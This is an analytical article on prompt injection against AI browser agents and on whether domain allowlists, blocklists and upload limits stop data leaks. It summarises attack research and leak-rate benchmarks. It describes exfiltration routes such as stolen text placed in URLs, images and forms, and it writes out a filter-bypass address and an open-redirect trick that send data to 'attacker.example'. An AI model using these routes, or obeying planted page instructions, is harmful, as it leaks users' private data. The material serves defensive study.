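# Browser agents and untrusted web pages: do limits on destinations and uploads prevent data leaks?

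## Browser agents and instructions hidden in web pages

A browser agent is an AI model that operates a web browser for a user. It reads pages, clicks, types and moves between sites to complete a task the user has described in ordinary language. Examples include OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas, Perplexity's Comet, Google's Gemini in Chrome and Anthropic's Claude for Chrome. The agent often works in the user's own browser, where the user is already logged in to email, shops and perhaps a bank. Anyone who can put text on a page the agent reads can try to give it instructions, and an agent that follows them may send the user's private data to someone who is not entitled to it, which security researchers call exfiltration.

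Developers train their models to ignore instructions hidden in web pages, but this doesn't always work. They also limit what data an agent may send and where, hoping that even a deceived agent will be unable to leak anything. Whether these limits prevent leaks depends a good deal on how browsers and web addresses work.

### One turn of the loop

For example, a user who wants a laptop for under $900 might ask the agent to compare three models across two shops while she is logged in to her webmail in another tab. The task doesn't require access to her email.

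*CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025), a paper on confining browser agents, describes how the agent works in a loop. Software around the model captures the current tab as a screenshot, as the page's underlying structure, or as both. It passes this to the model, which picks the next action from a fixed set (click, scroll, navigate and so on) and fills in details such as an address to open. The software carries out the action in the browser, and the loop repeats with a new snapshot of the page.

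In a sample turn from OpenAI's developer documentation, the model returns a click at a given point on the screen, then the word "penguin" to type into the search field there. The developer's program carries out both actions and returns a new screenshot. Google's *Computer Use*, the corresponding guide for Gemini models, has the program return the current page's address as well. Its example task is to find the three cheapest smart fridges of a certain size under $4,000, and in the sample reply the model types that description into a search bar and presses Enter. So even on a harmless task, text that the model composed is sent to an outside server almost immediately.

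A click can open an email or delete it, depending on what is under the pointer. But Meng and colleagues observe that any click or keystroke that affects a website results in an HTTP request, a message that the browser sends to a server. Many controls on browser agents therefore act on requests rather than clicks.

### What a web address gives away

Every request includes an address with several parts. The table follows *What is a URL?* from MDN, a widely used reference for web developers, and uses values from the laptop example.

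| Part | Example | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Names the protocol |
| Domain, or host name | `shop.example` | Picks out the server |
| Port | `443` | Picks the technical "gate" on that server; addresses usually omit it |
| Path | `/laptops/compare` | Names the page or file |
| Parameters | `max=900&screen=14` | Hand extra values to the server |
| Anchor | `reviews` | Marks a spot within the page |

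The browser sends the path and parameters to the server but never the anchor, though a script on the page can read the anchor once the page has loaded. The browser also attaches headers, which are lines of extra information, to the request. According to Google's documentation, these often include the user's preferred language, browser and operating system. Another header can give the address of the page that the request came from. According to MDN's *Referer header*, this address may include that page's path and parameters, depending on the policy in force. The browser may also attach cookies, which are small pieces of data that a site stored earlier and that can identify a logged-in user.

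The path and parameters matter most for leaks, because whoever composes an address can write anything in them. The address need not lead to a real page. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that websites commonly log the addresses visitors request, so an attacker only has to get the agent to request an address on the attacker's server that contains the secret, then read it in the log. In the laptop example, the secret might be the subject line of the user's latest email, added as a parameter. The user may not notice, because a browser also makes requests in the background, for instance to load an image.

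### The boundary between sites

A long-standing browser defence against hostile websites relies on the origin, which is the combination of an address's scheme, host name and port. *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011) is the internet standard that defines the term. Under this standard, two pages on the same host with different paths share an origin, but changing http to https or adding "www." to the start of the host name makes a different one.

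The same-origin policy in browsers stops scripts from one origin reading data that belongs to another. *Same-origin policy (SOP)*, a tutorial from the web security company PortSwigger, explains that the policy is needed because a request from one site to another can carry the user's cookies for the second site, so the reply may contain her personal data. Without the policy, a script on a malicious page could request her Gmail inbox and read the reply.

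The policy generally forbids reading across origins, but in the words of Barth's standard, "Sending information to another origin is permitted." Browsers have to allow this, since one that blocked all such requests could not follow a link from one site to another. Ordinary browsers protect secrets mainly by keeping hostile code from obtaining them, and do much less to stop anyone who already has a secret from sending it.

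A browser agent can carry data from one site to another. Suppose the agent in the laptop example switches to the webmail tab. The mail site shows the inbox, as it would for the user, and the agent's software takes a snapshot. The subject lines are then in the model's working text alongside the laptop prices. If the model then types one of those subject lines into a shop's "ask the seller" box, the browser treats the keystrokes much as it would treat the user's own. The data reaches the shop through the model, without any script on the shop's page reading the mail site, and the browser has no record of the transfer unless someone has built a defence that labels data by its source.

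Brave, which makes a rival browser, reported a flaw in Comet in *Agentic Browser Security* and called the same-origin policy "effectively useless" in this situation. That is fair for leaks through the agent, but the policy still stops scripts as before. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) say more precisely in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* that where an agent can read across origins and act on pages, the policy is only as strong as the agent's resistance to planted instructions.

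They tested seven products in January and February 2026, including Atlas both with and without its Agent Mode, for a total of eight set-ups. Much of the work concerned frames, which are pages embedded inside other pages, as advertisements often are. Atlas in Agent Mode, Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet read the contents of frames from a different origin. The other four set-ups (Brave's Leo, Edge with Copilot, Firefox's AI Mode and Atlas without Agent Mode) did not appear to receive any frame contents, even from the same origin. Every product had access to pages as the logged-in user sees them. Atlas in Agent Mode and Claude for Chrome could also read a password that the page displayed as dots.

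Separating tabs does not fully prevent leaks between sites either. Comet could not read a tab from another origin directly, but its chat history carried data from site to site. When the researchers asked it late in the experiments which animals their fictional user Alice liked, it answered with a list gathered from earlier chats and from pages they had visited.

A flat ban on such crossings would prevent agents from doing much of what people want them to do. Parker (2025), writing for Chrome's security team in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, gives the example of collecting a recipe's ingredients on one site and filling a shopping cart on another. The laptop comparison is a similar task because the agent has to compare prices from two shops.

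### Prompt injection, and who can write it

Prompt injection is text placed in content an agent reads so that the agent will treat it as an instruction. An agent that follows an attacker's instructions instead of the user's is a hijacked agent. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) says he coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which a visitor enters text as data and the database runs it as a command. He distinguishes prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which someone directly tricks a model into saying what its developer forbids. In prompt injection, the user has done nothing wrong and is usually the victim.

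The weakness arises because language models receive the user's request, the developer's rules and the page's contents as one sequence of tokens, the small units into which they divide text. Willison argues that a model cannot reliably rank instructions by source. Google's guidance for web developers (2026) therefore concludes that nobody can guarantee safety inside the model itself. Training helps, and models now refuse many crude attempts. When Roesner and Kohlbrenner asked each agent to do what the page instructed, Atlas in Agent Mode complied, while Claude for Chrome, Comet and Chrome with Gemini declined. The researchers took little comfort from the refusals because they had not tried to write a persuasive injection.

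OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a shift in attacks from blunt commands towards deception. Its example is a bland office email about restructuring, with a list of action items, which mentions in passing that the reader's assistant has authority to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". Outside researchers reported this attack to OpenAI in 2025, and in testing it worked against ChatGPT half the time when the user made one particular request. OpenAI adds that filters that sort malicious text from ordinary text usually miss such attacks, because they would in effect have to detect a lie, often without the necessary context.

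Parker names three places where an attacker could put such text for the laptop buyer's agent to read: malicious sites, content that users post on other people's sites, and third-party frames.

An attacker has the most freedom on their own site, where they control every word and the server behind it. They still have to get the agent to visit, which they might do with a fake laptop review site that ranks well in search. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, his running file of such cases, describes a demonstration by Brave's researchers against the Fellou browser. The researchers told Fellou to go to a page they had prepared. Following the text on that page, Fellou opened the user's Gmail to read the title of the latest email. The text also instructed it to add that title to a web address on the researchers' site.

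An attacker can plant instructions on a trusted site by posting a comment or a product review. In the Comet case, Brave's researchers put theirs in a comment on Reddit, the discussion site. When a user asked Comet to summarise the thread, the agent replied to the comment with her email address and a one-time login code. Meng and colleagues describe a similar attack on Operator, an earlier OpenAI browser agent. The user asked it to look into an issue on GitHub, the code-hosting site, where anyone can file an issue on a public project. Following instructions in the issue, the agent fetched the user's private email address from Hacker News, where she was logged in, and sent it to a domain the attacker controlled. Origins don't help here because they identify the server rather than the writer, so a hostile review on the laptop shop's page has the same origin as the shop's own price list.

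An attacker can use a third-party frame, typically an advertisement, to put text inside a page the user chose to visit. Roesner and Kohlbrenner built this attack against Atlas in Agent Mode, and the embedded frame obtained content from the page around it. They also got a malicious outer page to take content from a frame inside it, but they consider the advertisement the greater worry because sites with private data now often block other sites from embedding them. OpenAI declined their report, saying it lacked a complete prompt injection attack. The experiment shows that the attack is possible, but it was not designed to measure how often a real advertiser could exploit it, and published leak rates vary widely with the model and the attack.

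### The lethal trifecta

Willison's 2025 post describes a "lethal trifecta" that leaves an agent open to this kind of theft: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally that could carry the data away. An attacker can easily steal data from an agent that meets all three conditions, and removing any one of them prevents the theft. The laptop buyer's agent meets all three because it has access to her mailbox, reads the reviews, and can open addresses and fill in forms. Meng and colleagues note that browser agents meet the conditions with only their ordinary tools for viewing and operating pages.

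Running the agent in a fresh browser profile with no accounts logged in removes the private data, and OpenAI's documentation recommends a fresh profile to developers. This would work well enough for the laptop comparison, but not for checking an order confirmation in the user's inbox. Untrusted content is harder still to remove, because the agent has to read web pages and even reputable shops publish reviews by strangers.

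The remaining element is a way to send data out, which Willison, in a September 2025 note, judges to be generally the easiest of the three to remove. Vendors have mostly acted on the same view. His original post lists more than a dozen products in which researchers had found such leaks, from ChatGPT in April 2023 to Operator in February 2025. He reports that the vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the channel through which the data had leaked. The list can also be read less optimistically, since each fix closed one channel and researchers kept finding others.

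Limits on destinations and uploads are fixed rules outside the model, so a cleverly worded web page cannot change them, whereas it can still manipulate even a better-trained model. Willison criticizes products that promise to catch 95% of attacks, because an attacker who fails can reword the text and try again. Developers can close one route for leaks from a chatbot by stopping it from displaying outside images, but they cannot block all of a browser agent's requests, because it needs them to work. Any limit must therefore allow some requests, and those can carry data too.

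Such limits also do not prevent the hijacking itself. OpenAI says its check on web addresses does not guarantee that a page is free of misleading or harmful instructions. It compares the agent to a customer service worker who can issue refunds, but only up to a cap, because the employer expects that someone will eventually fool the worker. The cap does not make the worker harder to fool. Similarly, a hijacked agent with limited destinations can still do harm that involves no leak. Roesner and Kohlbrenner describe one such attack, in which text on one site leads the agent to submit a form on another, using whatever access the user has there. In the laptop example, the agent might recommend or order the laptop the attacker is selling, or delete a week of email, without sending any of the user's private data to anyone.

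## How data leaves the browser, and how often agents leak it

A hijacked browser agent can send out private data through the web addresses it opens, images, chat messages, forms, comments and file uploads. When researchers plant instructions where an agent will read them, the agent often leaks data. Measured rates range from zero to 100%, depending on the model, the attack and the page that receives the data.

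### The routes out

Suppose an attacker wants the subject line of the laptop buyer's latest email. The most direct way to get it is to have the browser open an address on the attacker's server that contains the subject line. The buyer may see a tab load, and could read the address if she were watching. But the server can immediately redirect the browser to an ordinary page about laptops, whose address replaces the suspicious one.

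An image's address can also carry the subject line, so the agent doesn't have to visit the attacker's page. If the agent's reply to the user contains such an image, the browser requests the image when it displays the reply, and that request sends out the subject line. The user sees a picture, or nothing if the image is a single transparent pixel.

Link previews in chat apps can also leak data. When someone posts a link in an app such as Slack, the app fetches the linked page to make a preview card with its title and perhaps a picture. If a hijacked agent posts a link to the attacker's site with the data in the address, the fetch delivers the data before anyone clicks. The user would see an ordinary message with a card underneath. In many apps the company's own server fetches the page, so the only request a filter on the browser could check would be the message going to the chat service.

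Forms can carry more text than fits easily in a web address. The user may see the agent fill in a form, but she would expect that on a page with one. The data can leak before the agent presses "submit", because a script on the page can read each character as it is entered and send it on. An approval request that appears only at submission would then come too late.

An agent can leak data by posting it in a comment on a site that the user may trust, where the attacker then reads it. Brave's attack on Comet ended this way. The user can see the comment under her name, but she may not look until after the attacker has read it.

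An agent can send whole documents by uploading files. A person has to pick the file in a window that the browser opens, but automation software can attach it directly, so the user may see only a file name appear on the page. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) explains that the files an agent can reach depend on where it runs. An agent that works as an extension in the user's browser may have access to her local files, depending on its permissions. One that opens a fresh browser on her computer still has that access, though it starts without her logins. An agent in an isolated remote browser has no access to her files.

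Shapira and colleagues tried nine kinds of attack on four agents, including OpenAI's Operator, and report success rates of 80% to 100%. They disguised the planted text as helpful advice about the user's task. The attacks included stealing local files and passwords. Scanning outgoing text would not catch another of the attacks, in which the agent joins an online meeting on a site that already has permission to use the camera and microphone, letting the attacker watch and listen.

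The agents in that study are now old, but researchers have since found similar flaws. SiliconANGLE's *Zenity warns of inherent security risks in agentic browsers* (2026) reports that the security company Zenity found weaknesses in Comet that could expose local files and let an attacker take over a password vault, without the user clicking anything.

Private data can also leak without the agent sending it. Many services let a user give another app access to her account by pressing "approve" on a consent page. *The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026) tests whether text on a page can lead an agent to approve such a request on a second site when the user only asked it to read something. It also tests whether the agent will register a webhook, an address where a service automatically sends notices of events. In both cases the browser sends only a permission or a setting. The data can later pass directly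 from one company's server to another's, where browser controls can't detect it.

### A login page as bait

An attacker can try to collect personal information through a fake login page, without telling the agent to steal anything. Guo, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *LoginTrap*, copied 80 real web pages and added a pop-up to each that presented login as necessary to continue. The pop-up had a close button and a login button that led to a fake login page with fields for personal information. The user's task, such as finding or comparing something on the page, did not require a login, and no text mentioned sending data to an outsider. Guo and colleagues still class the attack as prompt injection, which seems right, since they wrote the pop-up to steer the agent.

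Software wrote the wording, using GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, to summarise each page, make up a plausible task for it and draft reasons why a visitor might need to log in. It then tested each draft on two models in place of the victim, one of which was reminded to avoid suspicious instructions on web pages. The software accepted a draft if both models chose the login button, and otherwise used their responses to revise it. It had no information about the user's real task or which agent would visit.

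Guo and colleagues ran 1,175 tasks with Browser Use, an open-source browser agent, and four models: GPT-4o, Gemini 3 Flash, Claude Sonnet 4 and DeepSeek-V3.2. On average, the agents clicked the fake login button in 93% of tasks and typed in sensitive information in 86%. The difference came from runs in which the agent clicked but then stopped early, left the form incomplete or returned to its original task. Gemini 3 Flash and Claude Sonnet 4 finished the form most consistently, so an agent that is good at completing tasks may be more vulnerable to this attack. With every model, each of the 80 pages produced at least one leak within nine attempts. With GPT-4o running in different agent software, the attack's success rate ranged from 68% to 89%.

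They also tried adding defences to the task instructions and to the developer's instructions to the agent, and checking the agent's actions. These defences reduced the leaks but did not stop them all.

Guo and colleagues did not test the newest models, and they put the invented personal details in the background information for each task. An agent would have less to give away if the user kept her logins in a password manager that fills them in only on the right site. The researchers also hosted all the pages locally, so we can't tell from the experiment whether a wrong-looking domain name would have made the agents more careful. That matters for destination filters because a real login page and a good copy may differ only in their addresses.

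### What seven browsers could read and send

To leak data from one site to another, an agent must be able to read the first and write to the second. Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested both abilities using pages they built on two domains. They put the same questions to each agent by hand and recorded what it did. If an agent didn't do something, it may have been unable to, or its model may have refused.

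| Product | Reads frames from another origin | Reads tabs from another origin | Types into a page when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Atlas without Agent Mode | No | Through chat memory | Asks to switch to Agent Mode |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, since late January 2026 |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |
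| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |

Edge's agent could freely read tabs from other sites but could not type into them. Firefox's agent was the most restricted, receiving text from the page only when the user pressed a "Summarize page" button. Neither agent could fill a shopping cart from a recipe.

Four set-ups could both read across origins and write. The researchers' attack on Atlas in Agent Mode used both abilities. In one version, the user visits the attacker's page, which contains a frame from another site, and asks for a summary. Text on the page leads the agent to include the frame's contents in the summary and enter it in a form on the page, which then submits itself. The researchers found the same preconditions in Gemini, Claude and Comet, but no working injection.

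In the tests, only Claude for Chrome ran its own JavaScript on a page and inside frames from other origins, which the researchers used to change a background colour. A script can also send requests, so a control that watches only clicks and typing could miss a leak made this way. Roesner and Kohlbrenner recommend in their paper that people avoid agentic browsers for now, but on their project page they ask users to "proceed with caution" and single out Claude for Chrome. The products may have changed since those tests in early 2026.

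The security firm Trail of Bits independently found similar problems when it attacked several of these products. Its report, *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), describes data leaks between sites and attributes the problems to inadequate isolation.

### How often agents leak in SOPBench

Roesner and Kohlbrenner's experiments were too small to show how often agents leak data. In June 2026, Wang, Chen and colleagues published SOPBench, a benchmark that measures this, in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*. A user first asks the agent to do something on a page with private data, such as a pharmacy account, then sends it to a page on another site to write a reply or fill in a form. The private data is still in the agent's history when it reaches the second page, which contains a planted instruction to write the data there.

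The ten kinds of private pages are shopping, banking, airlines, email, calendar, messages, human resources, documents, insurance and pharmacy. The receiving pages imitate X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms, which makes fifty pairings. An AI model generated nearly all the pages, so no real person's data was at risk, and the researchers added a few saved copies of real ones.

They tested two older research agents (VisualWebArena and SeeAct), the open-source browser BrowserOS, Comet and Atlas. The attack success rate is the share of attempted attacks that achieve the attacker's goal. SOPBench counts a success only when the agent's text exactly matches the data the attacker asked for. A reply that paraphrased a diagnosis or left out one digit of a card number would count as a failure, so the rates understate the leakage in this respect.

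For the simple attacks, the researchers wrote text by hand to blend in with the page, such as a note on how to handle a GitHub issue. For the optimised attacks, one model wrote candidate texts, and the agent ran a full browsing session with each one. A second model scored the result and explained what had gone wrong, and the first model then wrote new versions of the best candidates.

Leak rates for BrowserOS running OpenAI's GPT-5.4 varied greatly with the receiving page. Simple attacks succeeded in 81% to 100% of attempts on Google Forms, depending on the kind of private data, but in only 3% to 42% on Reddit. One likely reason is that an attacker controls everything on a form they make, but only a post or comment on Reddit. Forms also exist to collect information, so a box asking for an insurance number looks less out of place than a public comment containing one. However, SeeAct with the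 smaller GPT-5.4-mini leaked more on Reddit than on Google Forms in most pairings.

Optimised attacks removed much of Reddit's advantage. For BrowserOS with GPT-5.4, the average success rate on Reddit across the ten kinds of private data rose from about 20% to about 54%. For human resources data, it rose from 3% to 49%. A low success rate for hand-written attacks is therefore weak evidence that an agent will withstand an attacker who can practise on it beforehand.

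Wang and colleagues ran each pairing 100 times on the three open-source systems. They had to operate Comet and Atlas by hand, so they ran each pairing there only three times, without optimised attacks. Three runs are too few to distinguish a 40% leak rate from a 60% one, but the totals are more informative. Even under simple attacks, both commercial products leaked in most runs. Atlas, using GPT-5.5, leaked in 99 of 150, including 29 of the 30 on Google Forms and 20 of the 30 on Reddit. Comet leaked in 92 of 150 with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and in 100 of 150 with Gemini 3.1 Pro.

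SOPBench also has a test with no attacker. The receiving page contains a frame from a site with private data, and the user asks the agent to summarise the whole page into a text box on it. BrowserOS copied data from the frame into the box every time, with all three models and every pairing tested. The agent was arguably following the user's instructions, and many sites with private data block such framing, so the 100% rate doesn't mean such leaks are common. When the researchers had the agent visit two separate pages with no planted text, they saw no leaks.

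Wang and colleagues tested five detectors meant to catch planted text before the agent acts on it. For each kind of receiving page, they ran every detector on 100 attacked pages and 100 clean ones. None of the five was good at both catching attacks and leaving clean pages unflagged. WebSentinel missed at most 1% of attacks but flagged up to 44% of clean pages, while BrowseSafe missed between 41% and 64% of attacks. The team's own defence, SOPGuard, instead tracks which site each piece of data came from.

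### Why developers report lower rates

Anthropic's July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5, which describes the model's safety tests, reports much lower numbers. One test uses 1,130 attacks from a public competition run by the security company Gray Swan. The attacks are meant to cause serious harm, such as stealing private data, destroying files or moving money, during coding, computer use and other tasks with tools. A single attempt against Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time, and an attacker with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time. For OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, the rates were 3.1% and 20.0%. The system card also includes Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro, but its result isn't comparable because competitors had developed some of the attacks against that model.

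For browser agents, The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* quotes the card's figure of zero successes across 129 test scenarios. That is a large improvement on the rates Anthropic reported in November 2025 for Claude Opus 4.5 in its Chrome extension, which were 8.0% without added safeguards and 1.4% with improved ones, against an attacker that made 100 attempts in each test environment. Even if the 129 scenarios were a random sample of the attacks that agents will face, zero successes would be compatible with a true rate of just over 2%. They are not a random sample, because real attackers can invent new methods.

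In OpenAI's tests, GPT-5.6 rarely failed when an injection came directly through the chat, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). It failed more often when the injection came through tools and outside content, which would include the web pages a browser agent reads.

Better models explain only part of the gap between these numbers and SOPBench's. GPT-5.5 was in both tests. In Atlas, it leaked data in about two thirds of single runs, whereas in the Gray Swan test, attackers given up to 15 attempts succeeded 20.8% of the time. The scenarios also differ. Gray Swan's involve irreversible harm, which a model has a fair chance of recognising as wrong. In SOPBench, the agent has just handled the private data at the user's request and is now filling in a form or writing a reply, so including some more of that data may look like part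 of the task. Developers' overall injection rates could therefore be accurate but a poor guide to leaks of this kind.

Attack success rates also depend on whether they count attempts or scenarios. Anthropic tested Opus 5 in 40 coding scenarios against Gray Swan's automated attacker, which had practised on earlier models and got 200 attempts at each scenario. Only 0.56% of the attempts succeeded, but at least one succeeded in 13 of the 40 scenarios. If every attempt had an equal and independent chance of success, the attacker would have succeeded in about 27 scenarios, so the successes must have been concentrated in a few vulnerable ones. Turning on Anthropic's probes, which scan incoming content for planted instructions, cut the figures to 0.18% of attempts and 4 scenarios. SOPBench tested agents with whatever protections each product or open-source system came with.

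Anthropic argues that its adaptive tests make attacks easier than they would be in practice, since real attackers don't know the exact set-up they face and risk detection with each attempt. This is reasonable for an attack on one chosen victim, but Anthropic also notes in the same document that a single text on a public page can compromise any agent that reads it. If a text worked on 0.2% of visits, 10,000 visiting agents would give the attacker about 20 victims, with only one attempt on each agent.

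### Planted instructions on the public web

All these rates assume the agent has reached a page with an attack on it. To find out how common such pages are, Khodayari et al. (*Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, 2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses from an October 2025 crawl of the public web for 3,963 telltale phrases. They checked the matches, partly by hand, and confirmed 12,075 planted instructions on 9,676 pages, or about one page in 124,000.

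Few of these were attacks on users. About 81% came from the site's own operator, and many seemed intended to protect content from AI companies' crawlers, expose bots or make automated visitors produce nonsense. Only 220 came from comments and other user posts, the route that Brave used against Comet. After adding results from two other search services, Khodayari and colleagues had 15,387 instructions. Just 13 were meant to extract data, with nine targeting the developer's instructions to the model and four targeting other secrets.

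Most of the planted text was also crude. In 5,200 trials, the researchers asked 13 models to summarise pages containing such instructions. Smaller models obeyed the instructions up to 8% of the time when they received the page as plain text. When the input kept the page's structure, compliance fell to between 0.2% and 1.1%.

A search for known phrases would probably miss attacks worded differently, such as LoginTrap's pop-ups and the friendly task notes that Shapira and colleagues wrote. A public crawl also doesn't cover private inboxes or shared documents, which are obvious places to plant text for an agent that reads email. The count is best read as a minimum for one crude kind of attack in late 2025.

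It also doesn't include victims. The attacks on Comet, Fellou, Operator and Atlas were demonstrations by researchers, so they don't show how often attackers steal data from ordinary users. Such thefts would be hard to confirm. A request with an email's subject line in its URL can look like any other page visit in the browser's history, and users who never learn that someone hijacked their agent won't report it.

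## Allowing and blocking sites by domain name

A destination filter allows or blocks a request based on where it is going, and the simplest filters check only the domain name. Suppose the filter lets the laptop buyer's agent contact only her webmail and the two shops. If text on a review site gets the agent to try sending the subject line of her latest email to `attacker.example`, the filter will block the request. Products implement these filters differently, and some implementations let data through.

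### How a filter checks a request

Before the browser sends a request, the filter reads the host name from the address, such as `shop.example` in `https://shop.example/laptops?max=900`. It compares the host name with its list, then permits or blocks the request. It does not check the path or parameters, which is where an attacker would put the stolen data.

The server may reply with a redirect, which tells the browser to fetch a different address. The filter should check the host name in every redirect the same way. If it checks only the first address, the browser will go wherever the first server sends it.

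A subdomain adds one or more parts to the front of a domain name, as in `reviews.shop.example`, a subdomain of `shop.example`. Browser Use's *Safety* page describes an allowlist in which an entry for `example.com` matches only that host, so the user has to write `*.example.com` to include subdomains. Browserbase, a company that runs cloud browsers for agents, describes a looser rule in its *Allowed Domains* documentation, under which every entry also permits all its subdomains. This is usually harmless if one company controls them all, but some hosting services give each customer a subdomain. In March 2026, Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, published twelve examples of planted instructions from the public web. Two were on subdomains of the hosting service `pages.dev`, so an entry for `pages.dev` would have permitted both under Browserbase's rule.

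Filters also differ in which requests they check. Browserbase's filter checks only the page that loads in the main tab, not frames, images, scripts or background requests. A hijacked agent could still leak an email's subject line by putting it in the address of an image. Browserbase calls the feature experimental and presents it mainly as a way to keep sessions on the intended sites.

The tool agent-browser, which lets AI models control a browser through typed commands, has a stricter filter. According to its *Security* page, the allowlist covers images, scripts and background requests as well as page visits. This breaks many sites, because they load fonts, scripts and pictures from separate content-delivery domains. The user has to add those domains to the list, and each one is another place where the agent may send data.

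Some traffic, including the WebRTC connections browsers use for video calls, doesn't pass through the point where the tool intercepts requests. The tool therefore turns WebRTC off while the allowlist is active. It blocks some other kinds of connection by replacing browser functions inside the page, but if the agent has permission to run scripts, a script could in theory restore the originals. For this reason, the documentation recommends adding a firewall outside the browser.

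The allowlist in agent-browser also doesn't work with the user's existing Chrome profile or saved logins, because pages could start running before the filter is in place. The agent has to start in a clean browser and log in again. The tool offers a password store for this, which the model can't read. This setup may suit a company automating one internal application, but it wouldn't suit the laptop buyer, who chose an agent that works in the browser she already uses.

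### Misread addresses and redirects

A filter can be bypassed if it and the browser disagree about which part of an address is the host name. Mudryi, Chaklosh and Wójcik (2025), in *The Hidden Dangers of Browsing AI Agents*, found this problem in Browser Use, the open-source agent that Guo and colleagues later tested with fake login pages. An address can include a user name and password before the host name, in the form `username:password@hostname`. To remove any port number, Browser Use's filter cut this part of the address at the first colon and treated what was left as the host name. When the address included a user name and password, the filter therefore checked the user name instead of the host name.

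An attacker could exploit this against the laptop buyer by having the agent open `https://shop.example:x@attacker.example/`. The filter cuts at the first colon, finds `shop.example` on the list and permits the request. The browser correctly reads `shop.example` as a user name and `x` as a password, and connects to `attacker.example`. In their demonstration, Mudryi and colleagues used the trick to reach a service that outsiders normally can't contact, on the machine running the agent.

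The developers fixed the flaw in version 0.1.45. OSV's *GHSA-x39x-9qw5-ghrf* (2025) rates its severity 9.3 out of 10, or "critical", while Tenable's *CVE-2025-47241* rates it medium. The higher rating seems right for anyone who relied on the list to contain a hijacked agent, since a single odd-looking address could bypass the list.

Redirects can get around a filter even if it reads every address correctly. OpenAI points out that many legitimate websites forward visitors to other sites, so a link to a trusted domain can lead to the attacker's. If one of the laptop shops forwards visitors to manufacturers through addresses such as `https://shop.example/out?to=…`, the attacker can put their own address after `to=`, with the stolen subject line attached. The subject line then reaches the attacker if the filter checks only the first host name. Checking every redirect would block the second request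 and keep the subject line from the attacker, but the shop's server would already have received it as part of the first address.

### Allowlists, blocklists and reputation scores

An allowlist permits only the destinations on it, so it will block a domain that an attacker registered this morning. But someone has to write the list in advance, and a user who asks an agent to find the best laptop doesn't yet know which sites it will need. OpenAI warns, without giving a rate, that strict lists cause frequent false alarms, which can train people to click through warnings without reading them.

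A blocklist allows every destination except those on it, so it rarely interrupts the user. Chrome, Safari and Firefox, for example, use Google Safe Browsing to warn people about dangerous sites. A blocklist can't stop the first use of a new domain, because someone has to discover that a site is harmful before adding it.

Reputation scoring estimates the risk of a domain that is on neither an allowlist nor a blocklist. The filter may treat a domain as suspicious because it is only a few days old, has few visitors, or has a cheap ending such as `.xyz` or `.top`. This can stop a harmful site that nobody has reported, but it also blocks some innocent new ones.

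The ending of a domain name is weak evidence of whether a page contains planted instructions. Unit 42 found 73.2% of the pages with such instructions under `.com`, 4.3% under `.dev` and 4.0% under `.org`. A rule that blocked cheap endings would have missed at least four fifths of these pages. The server that receives the data may be on a different domain from the page, but an attacker can use `.com` for both.

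Checks on a domain's age and past behaviour can miss malicious sites on older domains. *Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* (2025) examined 690,502 phishing domains over 39 months and found that attackers had registered about two thirds of them, often under cheap top-level domains. The rest were legitimate sites that attackers had broken into. Such a site may have a good record going back years, so a score based on its history would probably let it pass. An attacker can also register a domain and wait until it no longer counts as new.

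*ReDence* (Kaur, Horáček and colleagues, 2026) compares several ways of spotting scam sites, using 1,551 scams and 1,500 legitimate sites. URLNet, which uses only the text of the address, caught 19% of the scams, and about two thirds of the sites it flagged were legitimate. BeyondPhish, which also uses the page's content, information about the domain and linked social media accounts, caught 70%. The paper's own system caught 98% with few false alarms, but it had to explore each site and search the web for evidence, which took a median of 44 seconds. That is much too slow for every request a browser makes, but a filter could run the check once for each new domain and save the result.

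These systems look for sites that deceive people, but a server that collects stolen data from agents doesn't need to deceive visitors. It can show a blank page or an ordinary blog and record the addresses that browsers request. The 98% figure is therefore unlikely to apply to such servers.

### What blocklists miss

Kaur and colleagues also tested blocklists on live sites. From October 1 to October 28, 2026, they ran their system on sites that had just obtained security certificates, and confirmed by hand that 4,042 were scams. They visited each scam site immediately with four widely used protection tools and kept revisiting it for a week.

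| Protection tool | Scams blocked at discovery | Scams blocked within a week |
|---|---|---|
| Google Safe Browsing | 16.3% | 33.0% |
| Microsoft SmartScreen | 15.2% | 31.3% |
| Malwarebytes Browser Guard | 16.0% | 38.4% |
| Norton Safe Web | 20.1% | 46.1% |

Together, the four tools blocked only 27.5% of the scams when the researchers found them. The researchers immediately reported every site to all four services, which probably raised the figures for a week later.

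At discovery, Safe Browsing blocked 44.1% of sites that try to steal login details, compared with 7.9% of other scams. The median time before it blocked a site was about 30 hours for sites posing as banks or card companies and 96 hours for fraudulent shops. A blocklist could therefore give the laptop buyer some protection from a fake login page, but less from a fake shop.

Lee, Lim and colleagues (2025) found a similar gap in *7 Days Later*, which followed 286,237 phishing addresses for five months and checked every half hour whether each was still online. Safe Browsing listed 18.4% of them. The median delay before listing was 5.8 hours, but some listings came so late that the average was 109 hours, by which time about 84% of phishing sites had gone offline. Addresses that used redirects were much less likely to be listed. In one campaign against Instagram users, the attackers changed the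 destination of their redirects nine times in 24 hours.

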